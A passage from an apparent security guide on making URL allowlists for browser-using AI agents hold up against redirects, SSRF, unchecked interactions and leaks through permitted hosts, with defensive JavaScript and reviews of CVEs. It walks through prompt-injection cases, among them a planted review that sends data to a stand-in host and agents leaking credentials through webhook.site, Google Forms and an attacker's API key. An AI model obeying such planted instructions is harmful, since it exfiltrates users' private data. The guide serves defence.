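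1. **Parse the complete URL once, with a parser that follows the browser's rules.** In JavaScript, the built-in `URL` class implements the WHATWG standard. Python's `urlparse` does not, so a Python program needs an additional library, such as a binding to Ada, the parser that Node.js uses. No later step should go back to the text and search it for colons or slashes, as Browser Use's old function did. If the program assembles the URL from pieces, it should parse the assembled result. After parsing, refuse any scheme that the list does not permit.

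2. **Refuse userinfo.** A correct parser finds the right host even when a URL contains credentials, so this step is a second line of defence, in case another program in the chain reads the URL differently. It costs little, because few sites still expect a password in the URL. Where one does, the operator can usually give the password to the browser automation library separately.

3. **Normalise the host.** This means lower-case letters, numeric addresses in standard form and international names in their ASCII form, which begins with "xn--". A WHATWG parser does all of this. The entries on the list need the same treatment, and the simplest way to give it to them is to run them through the same parser when the program starts. A host name may also end in a dot, which the parser keeps. An allowlist can simply refuse such a name, but a blocklist has to treat it as the same host.

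4. **Compare whole labels, and compare the port.** For an exact entry, the two hosts must be equal. For an entry that covers subdomains, the host must end with a dot followed by the entry. The port must match too.

5. **Refuse on any error.** This includes a URL that does not parse, a host that is empty and an entry that the program does not understand. An exception in the check must never lead to the navigation going ahead.

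6. **Give the browser the parsed URL.** The parser can turn its result back into text, and the browser should receive that text and not the string that the model wrote. If the original contained something that two programs might read differently, the parser has already settled it. Apify's documentation tool did the opposite: it tested a string and then passed the same string to the function that fetches pages, which parsed it afresh.

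Another flaw in Apify's server illustrates the first two steps. The company's store offers ready-made scrapers called Actors, which outside developers can publish. According to Lutra Security's *Actor MCP path authority injection leaks Apify token* (2026), the server built an address by joining a trusted URL to a path from the Actor's definition, without checking where the result led. A malicious publisher could choose a path that turned the trusted host into userinfo and supplied a new host after it. When a user ran or merely inspected such an Actor, the server sent that user's access token to the publisher's machine. Checking the trusted URL before the join would not have caught this. Apify fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-50143, in version 0.10.11.

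The whole procedure fits in a short JavaScript function. Each allowlist entry is an object with a host name and port that the same `URL` class produced at startup, and a flag for whether the entry covers subdomains.

```js
function permittedUrl(text, entries) {
  let url;
  try { url = new URL(text); } catch { return null; }
  if (url.protocol !== "https:") return null;
  if (url.username || url.password) return null;
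  const listed = entries.some(e =>
    url.port === e.port &&
    (url.hostname === e.hostname ||
      (e.subdomains && url.hostname.endsWith("." + e.hostname))));
  return listed ? url.href : null;
}
```

The function returns either a URL for the browser or `null`, which means refusal. An empty list produces `null` for every URL, so a missing configuration file stops the agent from opening any page. For the advisory's URL, with example.com on the list, the user-name check returns `null` before the function compares hostnames. If someone removed that check, the comparison would still refuse the URL, because `url.hostname` is `localhost`.

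Few operators write this function themselves, but they can use the six steps to question a vendor or read a library's source. The most revealing question is which URL parsers the check and the browser use. If the parsers are different, the vendor should be able to explain what happens when they produce different results for the same URL.

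## Checking every step of a redirect

The function at the end of the previous section checks one URL, but redirects can send the browser through several during a single navigate command. The browser can therefore reach an unlisted host even if the function checks the first URL correctly.

### Kinds of redirect and why sites use them

In Chromium's terms, a server redirect happens when the browser receives a response code in the 300s before it has a page to show. Chrome DevTools' *Fetch Domain*, which documents an interface for controlling a browser's requests, lists the codes as 301, 302, 303, 307 and 308. The response's `Location` header contains the next URL, which the browser requests immediately.

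A client redirect happens after the first page has loaded, when a refresh tag in its HTML or a script sends the browser to another page. The redirect can come several seconds after the first page appears.

A library that watches for navigations can detect a client redirect because it starts a new navigation, whereas a server redirect happens within a navigation that the library may already have allowed.

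Most redirects are harmless, and many sites would not work without them. Redirects to another host happen most often during sign-in. In a 2020 bug report, copied in Lightrun's *[Feature] route handler to support redirects*, a tester clicked "Sign in" on the BBC's home page. The browser went to session.bbc.co.uk, which returned a 302 redirect to account.bbc.com. A sign-in page's URL often includes a return address so that the page can send the visitor back afterward.

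Sites also use redirects to count clicks. A link to an outside page leads first to an address on the site's own server, which records the click and forwards the visitor. Link shorteners work similarly, but the server stores the long address and looks it up when someone opens the short one.

A click counter or sign-in page becomes an open redirect if it forwards visitors to any address given in its URL. The site's developer can prevent this by accepting only known destinations, but the agent's operator can't tell from outside whether every page on an allowed site does this. OpenAI cites open redirects as a reason not to rely on lists of trusted sites. Link shorteners pose the same problem, since anyone can usually create a short link to any address.

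### One chain, request by request

Suppose that shop.example counts clicks through a page at `/out`, which forwards the visitor to whatever address follows `to=`. A planted review says that the current paper prices are behind one of these links and asks customers to add their town. The model follows the instruction and returns a command to open this URL:

`https://shop.example/out?to=https://other.test/prices?town=Leeds`

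1. The library checks the URL. The host is shop.example, the port is the default one and there is no userinfo, so the check correctly permits it.

2. The browser sends a request to shop.example, with the path, the query and the cookie that keeps the company logged in.

3. The shop's server answers with a 302 and the `Location` header `https://other.test/prices?town=Leeds`. It sends no page for the agent to read.

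4. The browser looks up other.test, connects to it and negotiates encryption.

5. The browser sends a second request, this time to other.test.

6. The server at other.test answers with a page, and the address bar changes to other.test. A check of the final address can run only now.

By this point the server at other.test has received the path and query, including the town. It has also received the network address that the agent's traffic comes from, the browser's headers (which include its version and preferred language), and any cookies that other.test set on an earlier visit. It has not received shop.example's login cookie, because the browser sends cookies only to the sites they belong to.

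If the agent submits a form and the server answers with a 307 or 308 redirect, the browser resends the form's contents to the new address. With a 301 or 302, browsers normally drop the contents and make a GET request. The browser also carries the original URL's fragment over to the new page if the redirect doesn't specify one, and a script on that page can read it.

Redirects can also carry headers that the operator adds, such as the access token that some operators attach to the agent's requests with Playwright. Playwright's *Route* is inconsistent about whether such a header is still sent after a redirect. Its entry for `continue`, which lets an intercepted request go ahead, states that added headers also apply to any redirects. Its entry for `fetch` recommends `continue` for adding headers to the original request only. It is safest to assume that the token goes wherever the redirect leads,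 so operators should not put a secret in a header added this way unless something checks every hop.

The server at other.test could respond with another redirect to the administration page at localhost:8080, and the third request would reach that page.

### Checking only the first URL

Open WebUI, a self-hosted chat interface for language models, had a flaw of this kind. One of its optional loaders, `SafePlaywrightURLLoader`, fetches web pages for searches and document collections by opening them in a real browser through Playwright. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2743* (2026), the loader looked up the URL's host and refused private addresses. It then passed the URL to Playwright's `page.goto`, which follows redirects by default, and nothing checked where they led.

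A public page could therefore redirect the browser to localhost, to another container on the same network or to the address where a cloud provider serves a machine's credentials. According to Corgea's *Open WebUI*, this worked even when `ENABLE_RAG_LOCAL_WEB_FETCH`, the setting that permits local fetches, was off. The flaw, CVE-2026-54018, has a severity score of 7.7 out of 10. An attacker needs an ordinary account on the server to submit a URL.

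The advisory lists 0.9.6 as the fixed version, but there is reason to doubt that this release closed the gap. The advisory recommends intercepting requests with a handler set up through Playwright's `page.route`, which it says would validate every request, including redirects. Miggo's *CVE-2026-54018* reports that the 0.9.6 patch uses such a handler for page navigations. But according to Playwright's *Page*, when a server redirects a request, the handler runs only for the original URL. On that description, the new handler would check the user's URL a second time but not the redirect's destination.

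OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3653* (2026) describes another gap in the same handler, which checked only the request for the page itself. A later release, version 0.11.0, closed that gap and also fetches each URL with automatic redirects turned off, validating every hop. Version 0.11.1 fixed a separate flaw in how the loader looked up host names, so operators who use this loader should run 0.11.1 or later.

Open WebUI's developers made the same mistake in code that fetches pages without a browser. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2755* recommends turning off automatic redirects in that code and checking each `Location` header in a loop. Open WebUI 0.9.5 instead blocks all redirects for these requests unless the operator enables them with `AIOHTTP_CLIENT_ALLOW_REDIRECTS`, according to release notes reproduced in alexlebens.dev's *chore(deps): update ghcr.io/open-webui/open-webui docker tag to v0.9.5* (2026).

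The problem returned when redirects were enabled. Miggo's *CVE-2026-88001* describes how the private-address check and the operator's own domain blocklist then inspected only the first URL. An operator who enabled redirects for one legitimate site would have weakened both protections for every fetch.

Playwright MCP's list of allowed origins has the same limit, but its documentation says that the list does not affect redirects and that people can deliberately work around it. If the list contains only `https://shop.example`, a direct command to open other.test fails, but the browser can still get there through a redirect from the shop's click counter. The documentation calls the list a convenience for catching unintended access, "not a security boundary". For real isolation, it recommends permissions in the client, the program that connects the model to Playwright MCP.

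The long-standing behaviour of `page.route` probably explains this limit. The tester in the BBC case was using Playwright 1.4.2 and had set up a handler for all requests, but it was not called for the one to account.bbc.com in Chromium, Firefox or WebKit. According to Lightrun's copy, a maintainer replied that this was "currently by design" and relabelled the report as a feature request. Another maintainer closed it three weeks later. A domain check built on `page.route` alone checks only the first URL, even if the handler's pattern covers every address.

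### Checking the final URL

Browser Use checks the allowlist again after a navigation finishes, at least in the fork whose code is on Glama, and a comment in the code gives redirects as the reason. If the browser has ended up at an address the list does not permit, the handler logs a warning, reports an error to the rest of the program and closes the tab. Operators should test whether their installed version does the same by permitting one test host and having it redirect to another that is not on the list.

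The fork logs an error of type `NavigationBlocked` both when it refuses a URL in advance and when it closes a tab afterward. Only the message differs. It is "Navigation blocked to disallowed URL" in the first case and "Navigation to non-allowed URL" in the second. An operator who sees the second message should assume that the unlisted host received everything in the URL.

In the running example, closing the tab in time keeps the false prices out of the prompt. But by then, other.test has received the town, and if the redirects continued to localhost:8080, the administration page has already handled the request.

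In another open-source agent, Hermes Agent, *fix(security): add SSRF protection to browser_navigate* (2026) adds a check for private and internal addresses before navigation and another on the final URL. If a public URL has redirected to an internal one, the browser goes to `about:blank` and the tool returns an error. The stated purpose is to prevent the model from reading the internal page through a later command. A check made after navigation can do no more than that. The change also makes the agent refuse all URLs if the module containing the check fails to load.

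Checking only the final URL misses hosts in the middle of a redirect chain. If other.test records the query and then redirects the browser back to shop.example, the final address is on the allowlist and the check passes. Some sites route their own links through an outside click-counting company this way, so such a chain would not look unusual in a log.

Client redirects can also get past an allowlist. If a library checks the address only once, as soon as a page has loaded, it can approve a page on shop.example moments before a script moves the browser to other.test. The library has to check the address after every navigation, including those the model did not initiate, and should check it again just before adding the page to the prompt.

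Checking every URL in a redirect chain isn't enough if the browser sends the requests without waiting for the results. Chromium's Safe Browsing, for example, checks every redirect URL for known dangers while the requests are under way, without delaying the requests or the redirects. It only stops the browser from reading and displaying the final page before the check is complete, and if that takes more than five seconds, the navigation resumes anyway.

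That is a reasonable choice for Safe Browsing, which must not slow down the web. An allowlist meant to keep data private has to hold the request itself until the check finishes, and it should refuse the request if the check times out. The table compares the designs by the three aims described earlier.

| Design | Keeps hostile text from the model | Keeps private data from unlisted hosts | Keeps requests off internal services |
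|---|---|---|---|
| First URL only | No, after a redirect | No | No |
| Final URL only | Yes, if it runs before the library reads the page | No | No, though the model may not see the response |
| Every URL, without holding requests | Yes, if the page waits for the result | No | No |
| Every hop, before the browser sends it | Yes | Yes | Yes, if the host name leads to the expected address |

The last row applies to the requests that the check covers. Clicks, pop-ups and subresources can need separate handling.

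### Holding each request until the check has passed

For Chromium-based browsers, the most direct tool is the Chrome DevTools Protocol, the interface through which outside programs control the browser. Its Fetch domain, the group of commands that deals with requests, can pause each request before the browser sends it. Chrome DevTools documents that this includes requests caused by redirects. With the purchasing agent, it works like this:

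1. Before the first navigation, the program sends `Fetch.enable` without any URL patterns, so the browser will pause every request.

2. The browser prepares the request to shop.example, pauses it and sends the program an event called `requestPaused`, which contains the URL. The program finds the host on the list and answers with `continueRequest`.

3. The shop's server answers with the redirect. The browser prepares a request to other.test, pauses it and sends another `requestPaused` event. A field called `redirectedRequestId` identifies the request that led to this one.

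4. The program does not find other.test on the list and answers with `failRequest`. The server at other.test never receives the request.

The code is short, because it can reuse `permittedUrl` from the previous section. In this example, `cdp` is a connection to one browser tab.

```js
cdp.on("Fetch.requestPaused", event => {
  const requestId = event.requestId;
  if (permittedUrl(event.request.url, entries)) {
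    cdp.send("Fetch.continueRequest", { requestId });
  } else {
    cdp.send("Fetch.failRequest",
      { requestId, errorReason: "BlockedByClient" });
  }
});
await cdp.send("Fetch.enable");
```

The browser holds a paused request until the program responds. If `permittedUrl` fails with an error, the request stays paused and the page stalls. The check also uses a URL that the browser has already parsed, so the browser and the check are much less likely to parse it differently.

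This version checks images and scripts against the same list as pages, so a shop that keeps its pictures on a host outside the list will appear without them. The `resourceType` option can limit the pauses to page loads, but then every other request goes out unchecked, which is how the later Open WebUI flaw arose.

Browser Use already controls its browser through this protocol. The handler in the fork uses it to close tabs, so a developer could check each step of a redirect in that handler without adding a new automation library.

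Playwright takes more work, because a `page.route` handler does not run again after a redirect. The handler has to fetch the URL itself with `route.fetch` and look at the response before the browser gets it. By default, `route.fetch` follows up to 20 redirects, but according to Playwright's documentation, setting `maxRedirects` to 0 turns this off. The handler then receives the redirect response, reads the `Location` header, combines it with the current URL if it is only a path, and checks the result.

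The handler's next step depends on the agent's purpose. Open WebUI's 0.11.0 fix repeats the fetch and the check until it reaches a page, then gives the browser that page as the response to the original request. This works for a program that only extracts text. It causes problems for an agent that logs in to sites, because the browser treats the page as coming from the first URL. A page from docs.example could load under shop.example's address, and its scripts would run as if they came from shop.example.

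An agent's handler can instead refuse the original request and have the library start a new navigation to the checked URL. The address bar then shows the right host, and the handler runs again for the next hop. This works for ordinary page loads but not for a 307 or 308 redirect after a form submission, because the new navigation does not include the form's contents. The DevTools Protocol is the better choice for agents that submit forms, because the browser follows the redirects itself and the program only approves or refuses each one.

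Interception also slows browsing. According to Playwright, turning on routing disables the browser's HTTP cache, so the agent downloads the same files again on each visit. This hardly matters for a purchasing agent that opens a few dozen pages a day.

Even when every hop is checked, the browser may connect to an address that was not checked. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-87996* describes this problem in Open WebUI's loader. Open WebUI looked up the host name and found a public address, but the browser then looked up the name again. Someone who controlled the host's DNS records could direct the browser to an internal service by giving a different answer the second time. Since version 0.11.1, Open WebUI has fetched pages through its own HTTP client, which looks up the name once and connects to the address it checked.

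This is harder to exploit with a short allowlist, because the attacker would need to control the DNS records of a permitted host. An agent that may visit any public site lacks this protection, since the attacker can use their own domain.

### Permitting sign-in without widening the list

Checking every step of a redirect blocks some chains that checking only the final URL would allow. For example, the agent can't follow a link on shop.example that passes through an outside click counter before returning to the shop. The operator can usually open the link by hand, copy the final address and give that to the agent. This is better than adding the click counter to the allowlist, because the counter would receive whatever a misled agent put into a URL.

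Sign-in redirects are harder to handle because the agent can't skip the intermediate hosts. Allowing every subdomain of a site may not be enough. In the BBC case, an allowlist entry for bbc.co.uk and its subdomains would have covered session.bbc.co.uk but not account.bbc.com, which belongs to a different domain.

Copying hosts from the address bar, as the earlier procedure suggests, may miss some, because a host that only sends server redirects never shows a page and its name may never appear there. The browser's developer tools list every request if the operator sets them to keep the log when the page changes. The operator can also run the interceptor with a test account and have it record each host without blocking any. The operator can then decide which hosts belong on the list before the agent uses a real account.

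Keeping the sign-in out of the agent's task is often the narrowest solution. A person signs in beforehand in a separate browser session, saves its cookies to a file and loads them when the agent starts. Playwright MCP has a documented `--storage-state` option for this. The agent's allowlist then doesn't need the sign-in hosts, and the agent never handles the password. The operator has to protect the file as carefully as a password, because anyone who has it can use the account until the session ends.

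Signing in by hand doesn't suit every service. Some end the session after an hour, and others occasionally send the browser back to the account provider to renew it. The agent then stops at a refused redirect until someone signs in again. That may be acceptable for a purchasing agent that runs once a day, but an agent that runs overnight probably needs the sign-in hosts on its allowlist.

Suppose docs.example adds single sign-on through an account provider at id.example. A plain allowlist entry for id.example would let the agent open any page there, including one that changes the account's settings. With the DevTools Protocol, the operator can write a narrower rule that permits only the sign-in path on id.example, and only when docs.example redirects the agent there. The program can check where a redirect came from by recording the host of each request under its ID, then looking up the ID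 in `redirectedRequestId`. The rule would then block an injected command to open id.example directly.

Such a rule won't work with every sign-in. Some services pass the browser on with a form that a script submits, and the rule would refuse this because it counts as a new request, not a redirect. `redirectedRequestId` is also marked as experimental in the protocol, and a browser update could change it. An operator who uses the rule should test the sign-in after each update, and switch to an allowlist entry for the exact host and path if the field disappears.

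Checkout also needs a test, because refusing a redirect doesn't cancel the request that triggered it. Many shops accept an order and then redirect the browser to a confirmation page. If that page is on an unlisted host, the agent sees only an error even though the shop has taken the order, so it may place the order again. The library's error message to the model should therefore state that the previous request went through and only the next page was refused. For purchases, stopping the task and having a person check the order history is safer still.

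## Covering requests that the navigate command does not make

In an ordinary shopping task, the model might issue two or three navigate commands while the browser sends several hundred requests. Most of those requests start with a click or something on the page, so a check that runs only on navigate commands misses them, however carefully it compares URLs.

### How a browser comes to contact a host

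Some actions load a new page, in the same tab or in another one:

- A click can follow a link, whose URL is in the page's HTML. It can also run a script that chooses the destination only at that moment.
- A key press can have the same effects. Pressing Enter in a search box usually submits the form, and a script can react to any other key.
- Submitting a form sends what the agent typed to the address that the form specifies. That address may be on a different host from the page.
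- A pop-up is a new tab or window that a link or script opens. The browser may send its first request before the library has attached any checks to it.

Other requests leave the address bar unchanged:

- A frame is a page inside another page, often from another host. It loads without any action by the agent, and can later move to a new address by itself.
- The browser requests images and scripts as soon as it finds them in the HTML. A script then has the same access to the page as the site's own code.
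- Scripts make background requests to fetch or send data, for example to suggest products while the agent is typing.
- A service worker is a script that a site installs in the browser, separate from any page. It can answer requests from the site's pages or make its own, and it stays installed after the tab closes.
- With a speculative connection, the browser guesses which host it will need next and connects in advance. It sends no path or query, but the host learns the agent's network address.

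Each of these requests can defeat one of the aims of an allowlist without any visible sign. If the purchasing agent mistakenly types the company's delivery address into the search box on shop.example, the shop's page may, in normal operation, pass the text to an analytics company. An advertisement in a frame from other.test can put text into the model's prompt if the library includes text from frames. An image tag can cause a request to localhost:8080, just as a page load can, unless the browser itself blocks such requests.

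### OpenClaw's advisories from version 2026.4.8 to 2026.5.26

OpenClaw's developers published at least nine advisories in 2026 about browser commands that bypassed the product's address policy. That policy mainly blocks private and internal destinations, while an allowlist blocks everything it doesn't name. The flaws are still relevant to allowlists because they involved when the check ran, not what it compared.

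OpenClaw's agent controls the browser through several commands. The `act` command covers clicks, typing and similar interactions, including `evaluate`, which runs JavaScript in the page. A snapshot returns the page's content to the model. In the advisories, a route is the code that handles a particular command. Each route needs to apply the policy.

PT Security's *PT-2026-25422 · Npm · Openclaw* describes an earlier flaw that let someone with valid credentials and access to the browser tool read files on OpenClaw's machine. The developers blocked schemes such as `file:` and `data:` in a fix planned for version 2026.2.21. The fix protected direct navigation, but clicks and scripts could still take the browser to other URLs.

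CIRCL's *OpenClaw has Browser SSRF Policy Bypass via Interaction-Triggered Navigation* (2026) reproduces the advisory for CVE-2026-41912, which appeared on April 9. In OpenClaw, interactions with a page could trigger navigations that skipped the normal checks. The flaw affected versions up to 2026.4.5, and the developers fixed it in 2026.4.8. The advisory mentions new regression tests, meant to catch the flaw if it returns, but doesn't describe the code for the fix.

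OpenClaw 2026.4.9 fixed CVE-2026-43577, a flaw that let callers read local files through the browser. Corgea's *Browser interaction routes could pivot into local CDP and regain file reads* describes the flaw. An interaction could take the browser to the local address of the Chrome DevTools Protocol, and from there a caller could open `file:` pages that OpenClaw refused to open directly. According to PT Security, the fix checks the browser's URL again after an interaction causes a navigation and blocks the destination if it violates the policy.

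Three more fixes followed in version 2026.4.10:

- Some key-press and typing commands, including those that submit a form, did not get the full check after the action (CVE-2026-43580). GCVE's *OpenClaw* (2026) describes the fix as a "three-phase interaction navigation guard", without explaining the phases.
- In existing-session mode, commands could navigate or interact without the checks that applied elsewhere (CVE-2026-43573). The developers added policy checks to those routes, according to Corgea's *OpenClaw*.
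- The commands that select or close a tab could operate on a tab without applying the policy (CVE-2026-42439). The fix enforces the policy in both commands. Corgea gives this flaw a severity score of 8.5 out of 10.

The existing-session flaw is the most worrying of the three for operators who use that mode, because the mode connects the agent to a browser that is already running, possibly one logged in to a person's accounts.

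These April fixes may have protected fewer installations than their number suggests, because OpenClaw did not tighten its permissive default policy until version 2026.4.14, according to Corgea. A check added to the form-submission route cannot block a request to a destination that the policy permits.

### Flaws in commands that read a page

Version 2026.4.14 also fixed a flaw in how OpenClaw returned page content. According to GCVE's *Browser snapshot and screenshot routes could expose internal page content after navigation* (2026), the snapshot, screenshot and tab commands did not consistently check where the browser had ended up, so a caller could receive content from an internal page that the policy should have blocked.

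The debugging and export commands had a similar problem. If a blocked internal page was already open in a tab, a caller could refer to that tab and inspect or export its content. OSV's *OpenClaw < 2026.4.29* (2026) lists this as CVE-2026-35673, fixed in version 2026.4.29.

CVE-2026-53812 combined both kinds of problem, an unchecked navigation and an unchecked read. Corgea's *OpenClaw's browser act interactions could bypass private-network navigation checks* describes the sequence, which would look like this with the administration page from the running example:

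1. The agent is on a page that an attacker controls. A direct command to open localhost:8080 would fail, because OpenClaw checks that command's URL.
2. The agent clicks something on the page, and OpenClaw's initial check finds nothing wrong.
3. The click causes the tab to move to localhost:8080 after that check has finished.
4. A later `evaluate` command runs in the tab and reads the administration page.

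The developers fixed this in version 2026.5.18. The version numbers appear to be release dates, which would put this fix almost six weeks after the first fix for interactions. For users who could not upgrade immediately, the developers recommended restricting browser control to trusted operators and not using it on untrusted pages when sensitive internal services are within reach.

According to the advisory, an attacker needs authenticated access to browser control. The agent already has this access in normal use, so an attacker who plants a review that gets the model to click a button and then read the result may not need any other credentials. Operators therefore should not dismiss the advisory because of the access requirement.

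INCIBE's *CVE-2026-62227* (2026), published on July 17, describes another flaw in the snapshot routes, which again failed to check the destination after a navigation. It affects versions from 2026.4.14, the release that fixed the earlier snapshot flaw, up to but not including 2026.5.26. Operators who installed the April fix were still exposed, either because it was incomplete or because the same release introduced a new gap.

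Only version 2026.5.26 and later include all of these fixes. Operators should follow OpenClaw's releases rather than wait for vulnerability databases, which can be weeks behind. For example, the record for CVE-2026-53812 in OSV (2026) dates from June 11, more than three weeks after the apparent release date of the version that fixed it.

### Why guarding one route at a time falls short

Most of these fixes added a check to a command after someone showed that it lacked one. This approach works only if the developers know every command that can send the browser to another page, and remember to consider whether a command can do so each time they add or change one. They also have to cover the commands that read from the browser. Four of the nine flaws involved commands that could use a page the browser had already reached, so even a perfect check on clicking would not have fixed them.

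A product without such advisories is not necessarily safer. At least four of the nine credit Keen Security Lab, a research group at the Chinese company Tencent, so there are so many partly because skilled people were looking. None of the advisories reports an attack. GCVE's *OpenClaw < 2026.4.10* (2026) includes a May 7 assessment of the key-press flaw by CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, that lists no known exploitation.

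The better design checks every request before the browser sends it. Clicks, key presses and form submissions can only reach a host by making a request, so this check doesn't need to know which command caused the request. A second check should run just before any page content goes to the model, whether as a snapshot, a screenshot or the result of a script. Both checks then cover new commands automatically.

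### What OpenClaw's documentation now promises

OpenClaw has moved part of the way toward that design. An earlier copy of its documentation describes checks only for direct navigation and for opening a tab, each followed by another check of the final URL where possible. The current version adds interception during clicks, hovering, dragging, scrolling, selecting, key presses, typing, form filling and `evaluate`.

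During these interactions, OpenClaw intercepts page loads, including loads in frames. If the policy forbids the destination, OpenClaw blocks the load before the browser sends any of the HTTP request. It keeps intercepting loads for a limited time after each interaction, because a page may respond to a click after a slight delay. It then checks the final URL again if it can.

Suppose the agent clicks "Show all reviews" and a script on the page responds by trying to open localhost:8080. OpenClaw blocks the request if the script acts immediately, but the request can reach the administration page if the script acts after the limited period has ended. The documentation doesn't specify how long the period lasts, and lengthening it would reduce the gap without closing it.

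According to OpenClaw's *Browser configuration*, the interception misses redirect hops, a pop-up's first request, service worker traffic, some background requests and subresources, and page code that runs after the limited period. OpenClaw therefore calls its page routing "not a network firewall" and recommends network isolation or a proxy for complete prevention.

Refusing a request also doesn't prevent the browser from connecting to the host in advance. OpenClaw's developers observed Chromium opening speculative connections for page loads that the policy then refused. OpenClaw now tries to turn off the prediction feature that opens these connections each time it launches its own copy of Chrome. The setting may be missing if the browser kept running while OpenClaw's control service restarted, or if the agent connects to the browser in another way.

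The advice to use a proxy may be hard to follow in OpenClaw, because its own Chrome ignores the usual proxy environment variables, such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, and connects directly. An operator can pass Chrome's proxy options explicitly, but OpenClaw's strict mode blocks them unless the operator also permits private-network access. This conflict between the proxy setting and the strict address policy is one reason to enforce the restriction in the surrounding network instead.

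### Browserbase's narrower rule

Browserbase applies its allowlist only to top-frame navigations. Its documentation doesn't specifically mention navigations started by a click or a script, but it makes no exception for them, so they should be covered too.

Leaving frames unchecked helps with shopping, because a payment form that shop.example embeds in a frame from pay.example loads without an allowlist entry for pay.example. But frames from any other host load too, and the agent may be able to type into them. Anything it submits there can go to the frame's host while the top frame stays on shop.example, so the allowlist has no navigation to block.

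Browserbase also does not apply the list to URLs with schemes such as `file://` and `chrome://`, or to `about:blank`. The blank page is harmless, but `file://` URLs refer to files on the machine that runs the browser. Browserbase runs its browsers on its own machines, so a user's local files are not directly at risk, but anything the user has placed on the remote machine might be.

The table below is based on the OpenClaw advisories, OpenClaw's current documentation and Browserbase's page on allowed domains. "Not stated" means these sources don't address the case, so an operator has to test it. The checks listed for OpenClaw apply its address policy, which permits public sites by default.

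| Kind of request | OpenClaw | Browserbase |
|---|---|---|
| Direct navigate command | Checked before the request | Blocked if the host is not on the list |
| Click, key press or form submission that loads a page in the same tab | Intercepted during the action and for a limited time afterward | Top-frame navigations checked; these causes not named |
| Page load that a script starts later | Can get past the interception | Top-frame navigations checked; this cause not named |
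| Redirect hop | Can get past the interception | Not stated |
| First request of a pop-up | Can get past the interception | Not stated |
| Page load in a frame | Intercepted during the action and for a limited time afterward | Not blocked |
| Images and scripts | Some can get past the interception | Not blocked |
| Background requests | Some can get past the interception | Not blocked |
| Service worker traffic | Can get past the interception | Not stated |
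| Speculative connection | Turned off where possible when OpenClaw launches Chrome | Not stated |
| `file:` URL | Blocked for direct navigation; version 2026.4.9 fixed a way around this | List not applied |

More entries in OpenClaw's column involve a check, but most of those checks depend on timing or on how the browser started. Browserbase covers less, but an operator can more easily predict what it will miss. Neither product's allowlist or address policy is enough by itself to keep private data from reaching unlisted hosts. Browserbase's rule may be adequate for an agent that only reads public pages, if the operator accepts text from frames as part of the permitted page.

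### Extending an interceptor to the other requests

Developers can close several of these gaps inside the browser by writing an interceptor. The DevTools Protocol example in the previous section pauses images, scripts and most background requests as well as page loads, and it has no time limit. But it is connected to a single tab, so a pop-up opens in a new tab with no interceptor.

The protocol's `Target.setAutoAttach` command can connect the program to new tabs automatically. With the option `waitForDebuggerOnStart`, each new tab stays paused until the program connects and resumes it. During that pause, the program can send `Fetch.enable` to intercept the tab's first request as well. It has to send `setAutoAttach` once for the whole browser and again for each tab, because frames and workers can have their own connections. If the agent never needs a second tab, closing every new tab while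 it is still paused is simpler.

Service workers are usually easier to turn off than to monitor. Setting Playwright's `serviceWorkers` option to `"block"` prevents sites from installing them. Sites mostly use them for notifications and offline access, so a purchasing agent is unlikely to need them. Starting each task with a fresh browser profile also removes any that a site installed earlier, along with old tabs that a command might otherwise reuse.

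On managed computers, setting Chrome's `NetworkPredictionOptions` policy to 2 turns off the prediction that opens speculative connections. WebSockets, the long-lived connections that sites use for chat and live updates, may not trigger the interceptor, so they need a separate test with the installed browser version.

Once the interceptor covers everything, the allowlist may be too strict for real sites. Suppose shop.example keeps its product pictures on images.example. Adding that host to the main list makes the pictures appear, but also lets the agent open any page there. The operator can avoid this with two lists, one for pages and frames and one for everything they load. In the earlier code, one extra line chooses between them:

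```js
const list = event.resourceType === "Document" ? pages : resources;
```

The handler then passes `list` to `permittedUrl` instead of `entries`. The browser labels both top-level pages and frames as "Document", so the payment frame from pay.example needs an entry in `pages`. The entry for images.example goes in `resources`.

To set up the `resources` list, the operator runs the purchasing task with a test account, records which requests the interceptor refuses, and adds only the hosts that the task fails without. Advertising and analytics hosts can usually stay blocked. Scripts need more caution than images, because a script from an outside host can read what the agent types on the page and change where a button leads. If the shop works without a script, the operator should leave its host off the list.

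## Stopping data from leaving through permitted addresses

Even if the interceptor blocks every request to a host outside the operator's lists, an agent can still send company data to a permitted host. For example, an attacker could post a review on shop.example that tells customers to type their delivery address into the shop's search box to see local prices. If the purchasing agent follows the instruction, the browser opens a results page with the company's address in the URL's query string. The check correctly permits the request because shop.example is on the list.

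OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that sites commonly keep the URLs they receive in their analytics and server logs. A domain allowlist determines which hosts receive the data in a URL first, but it doesn't limit how much data fits in the path or query, or who can read it after it arrives.

### Permitted hosts that pass data to strangers

Some websites, such as webhook.site, let anyone create an address and see the requests sent to it. Developers use webhook.site for testing, and it was on the default browser allowlist of Antigravity, Google's code editor with built-in AI agents.

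PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* demonstrates a leak through a permitted address. A user gave Gemini, the model in the Antigravity editor, a link to an online integration guide that contained instructions in one-point type. Gemini followed them and collected code and cloud credentials from the user's project. A default setting was meant to keep Gemini from reading the credentials file, but it printed the file with a terminal command. It then put the code and credentials into the query of a webhook.site URL and had a second agent open that URL in the browser. The allowlist permitted the visit, and the credentials appeared in the attacker's log.

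PromptArmor did not report this privately because Google already warned users about data exfiltration during the editor's setup. PromptArmor mentions no fix. According to Agentpedia, a secondary source, webhook.site was still on the default list in March 2026. Antigravity users can open the list from the settings menu and should remove webhook.site if it is there. Operators should read a product's default list as carefully as one written in-house.

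A permitted host can also leak data through a service the operator didn't consider. The programmer Simon Willison describes a case in Superhuman AI, an email assistant. Its Content Security Policy (CSP) allowed images from docs.google.com. A CSP tells the browser which hosts a page may load things from. But docs.google.com also serves Google Forms, and a form can store data that arrives in a request for an image. A malicious email made the assistant send the contents of dozens of other messages to an attacker's form. Superhuman treated the report as a high-priority incident and issued a fix.

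In the running example, docs.example might offer forms as well as document storage. Its allowlist entry would then also permit forms that belong to anyone with an account there. If the company's files are all under one path, the operator can add a `url.pathname` check to `permittedUrl` to block the rest of the site.

Even restricting requests to an exact path may not stop data from leaving. Claude Cowork, an Anthropic product that works with a user's files, limits outgoing traffic to a list of domains, which included Anthropic's API. According to Willison, PromptArmor planted instructions that contained an attacker's Anthropic API key, and the agent used that key to upload the user's files to the attacker's account through the permitted host. A legitimate upload would have used the same host and path, so a filter also has to check the key and accept only the user's own.

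### A permitted domain that changed hands

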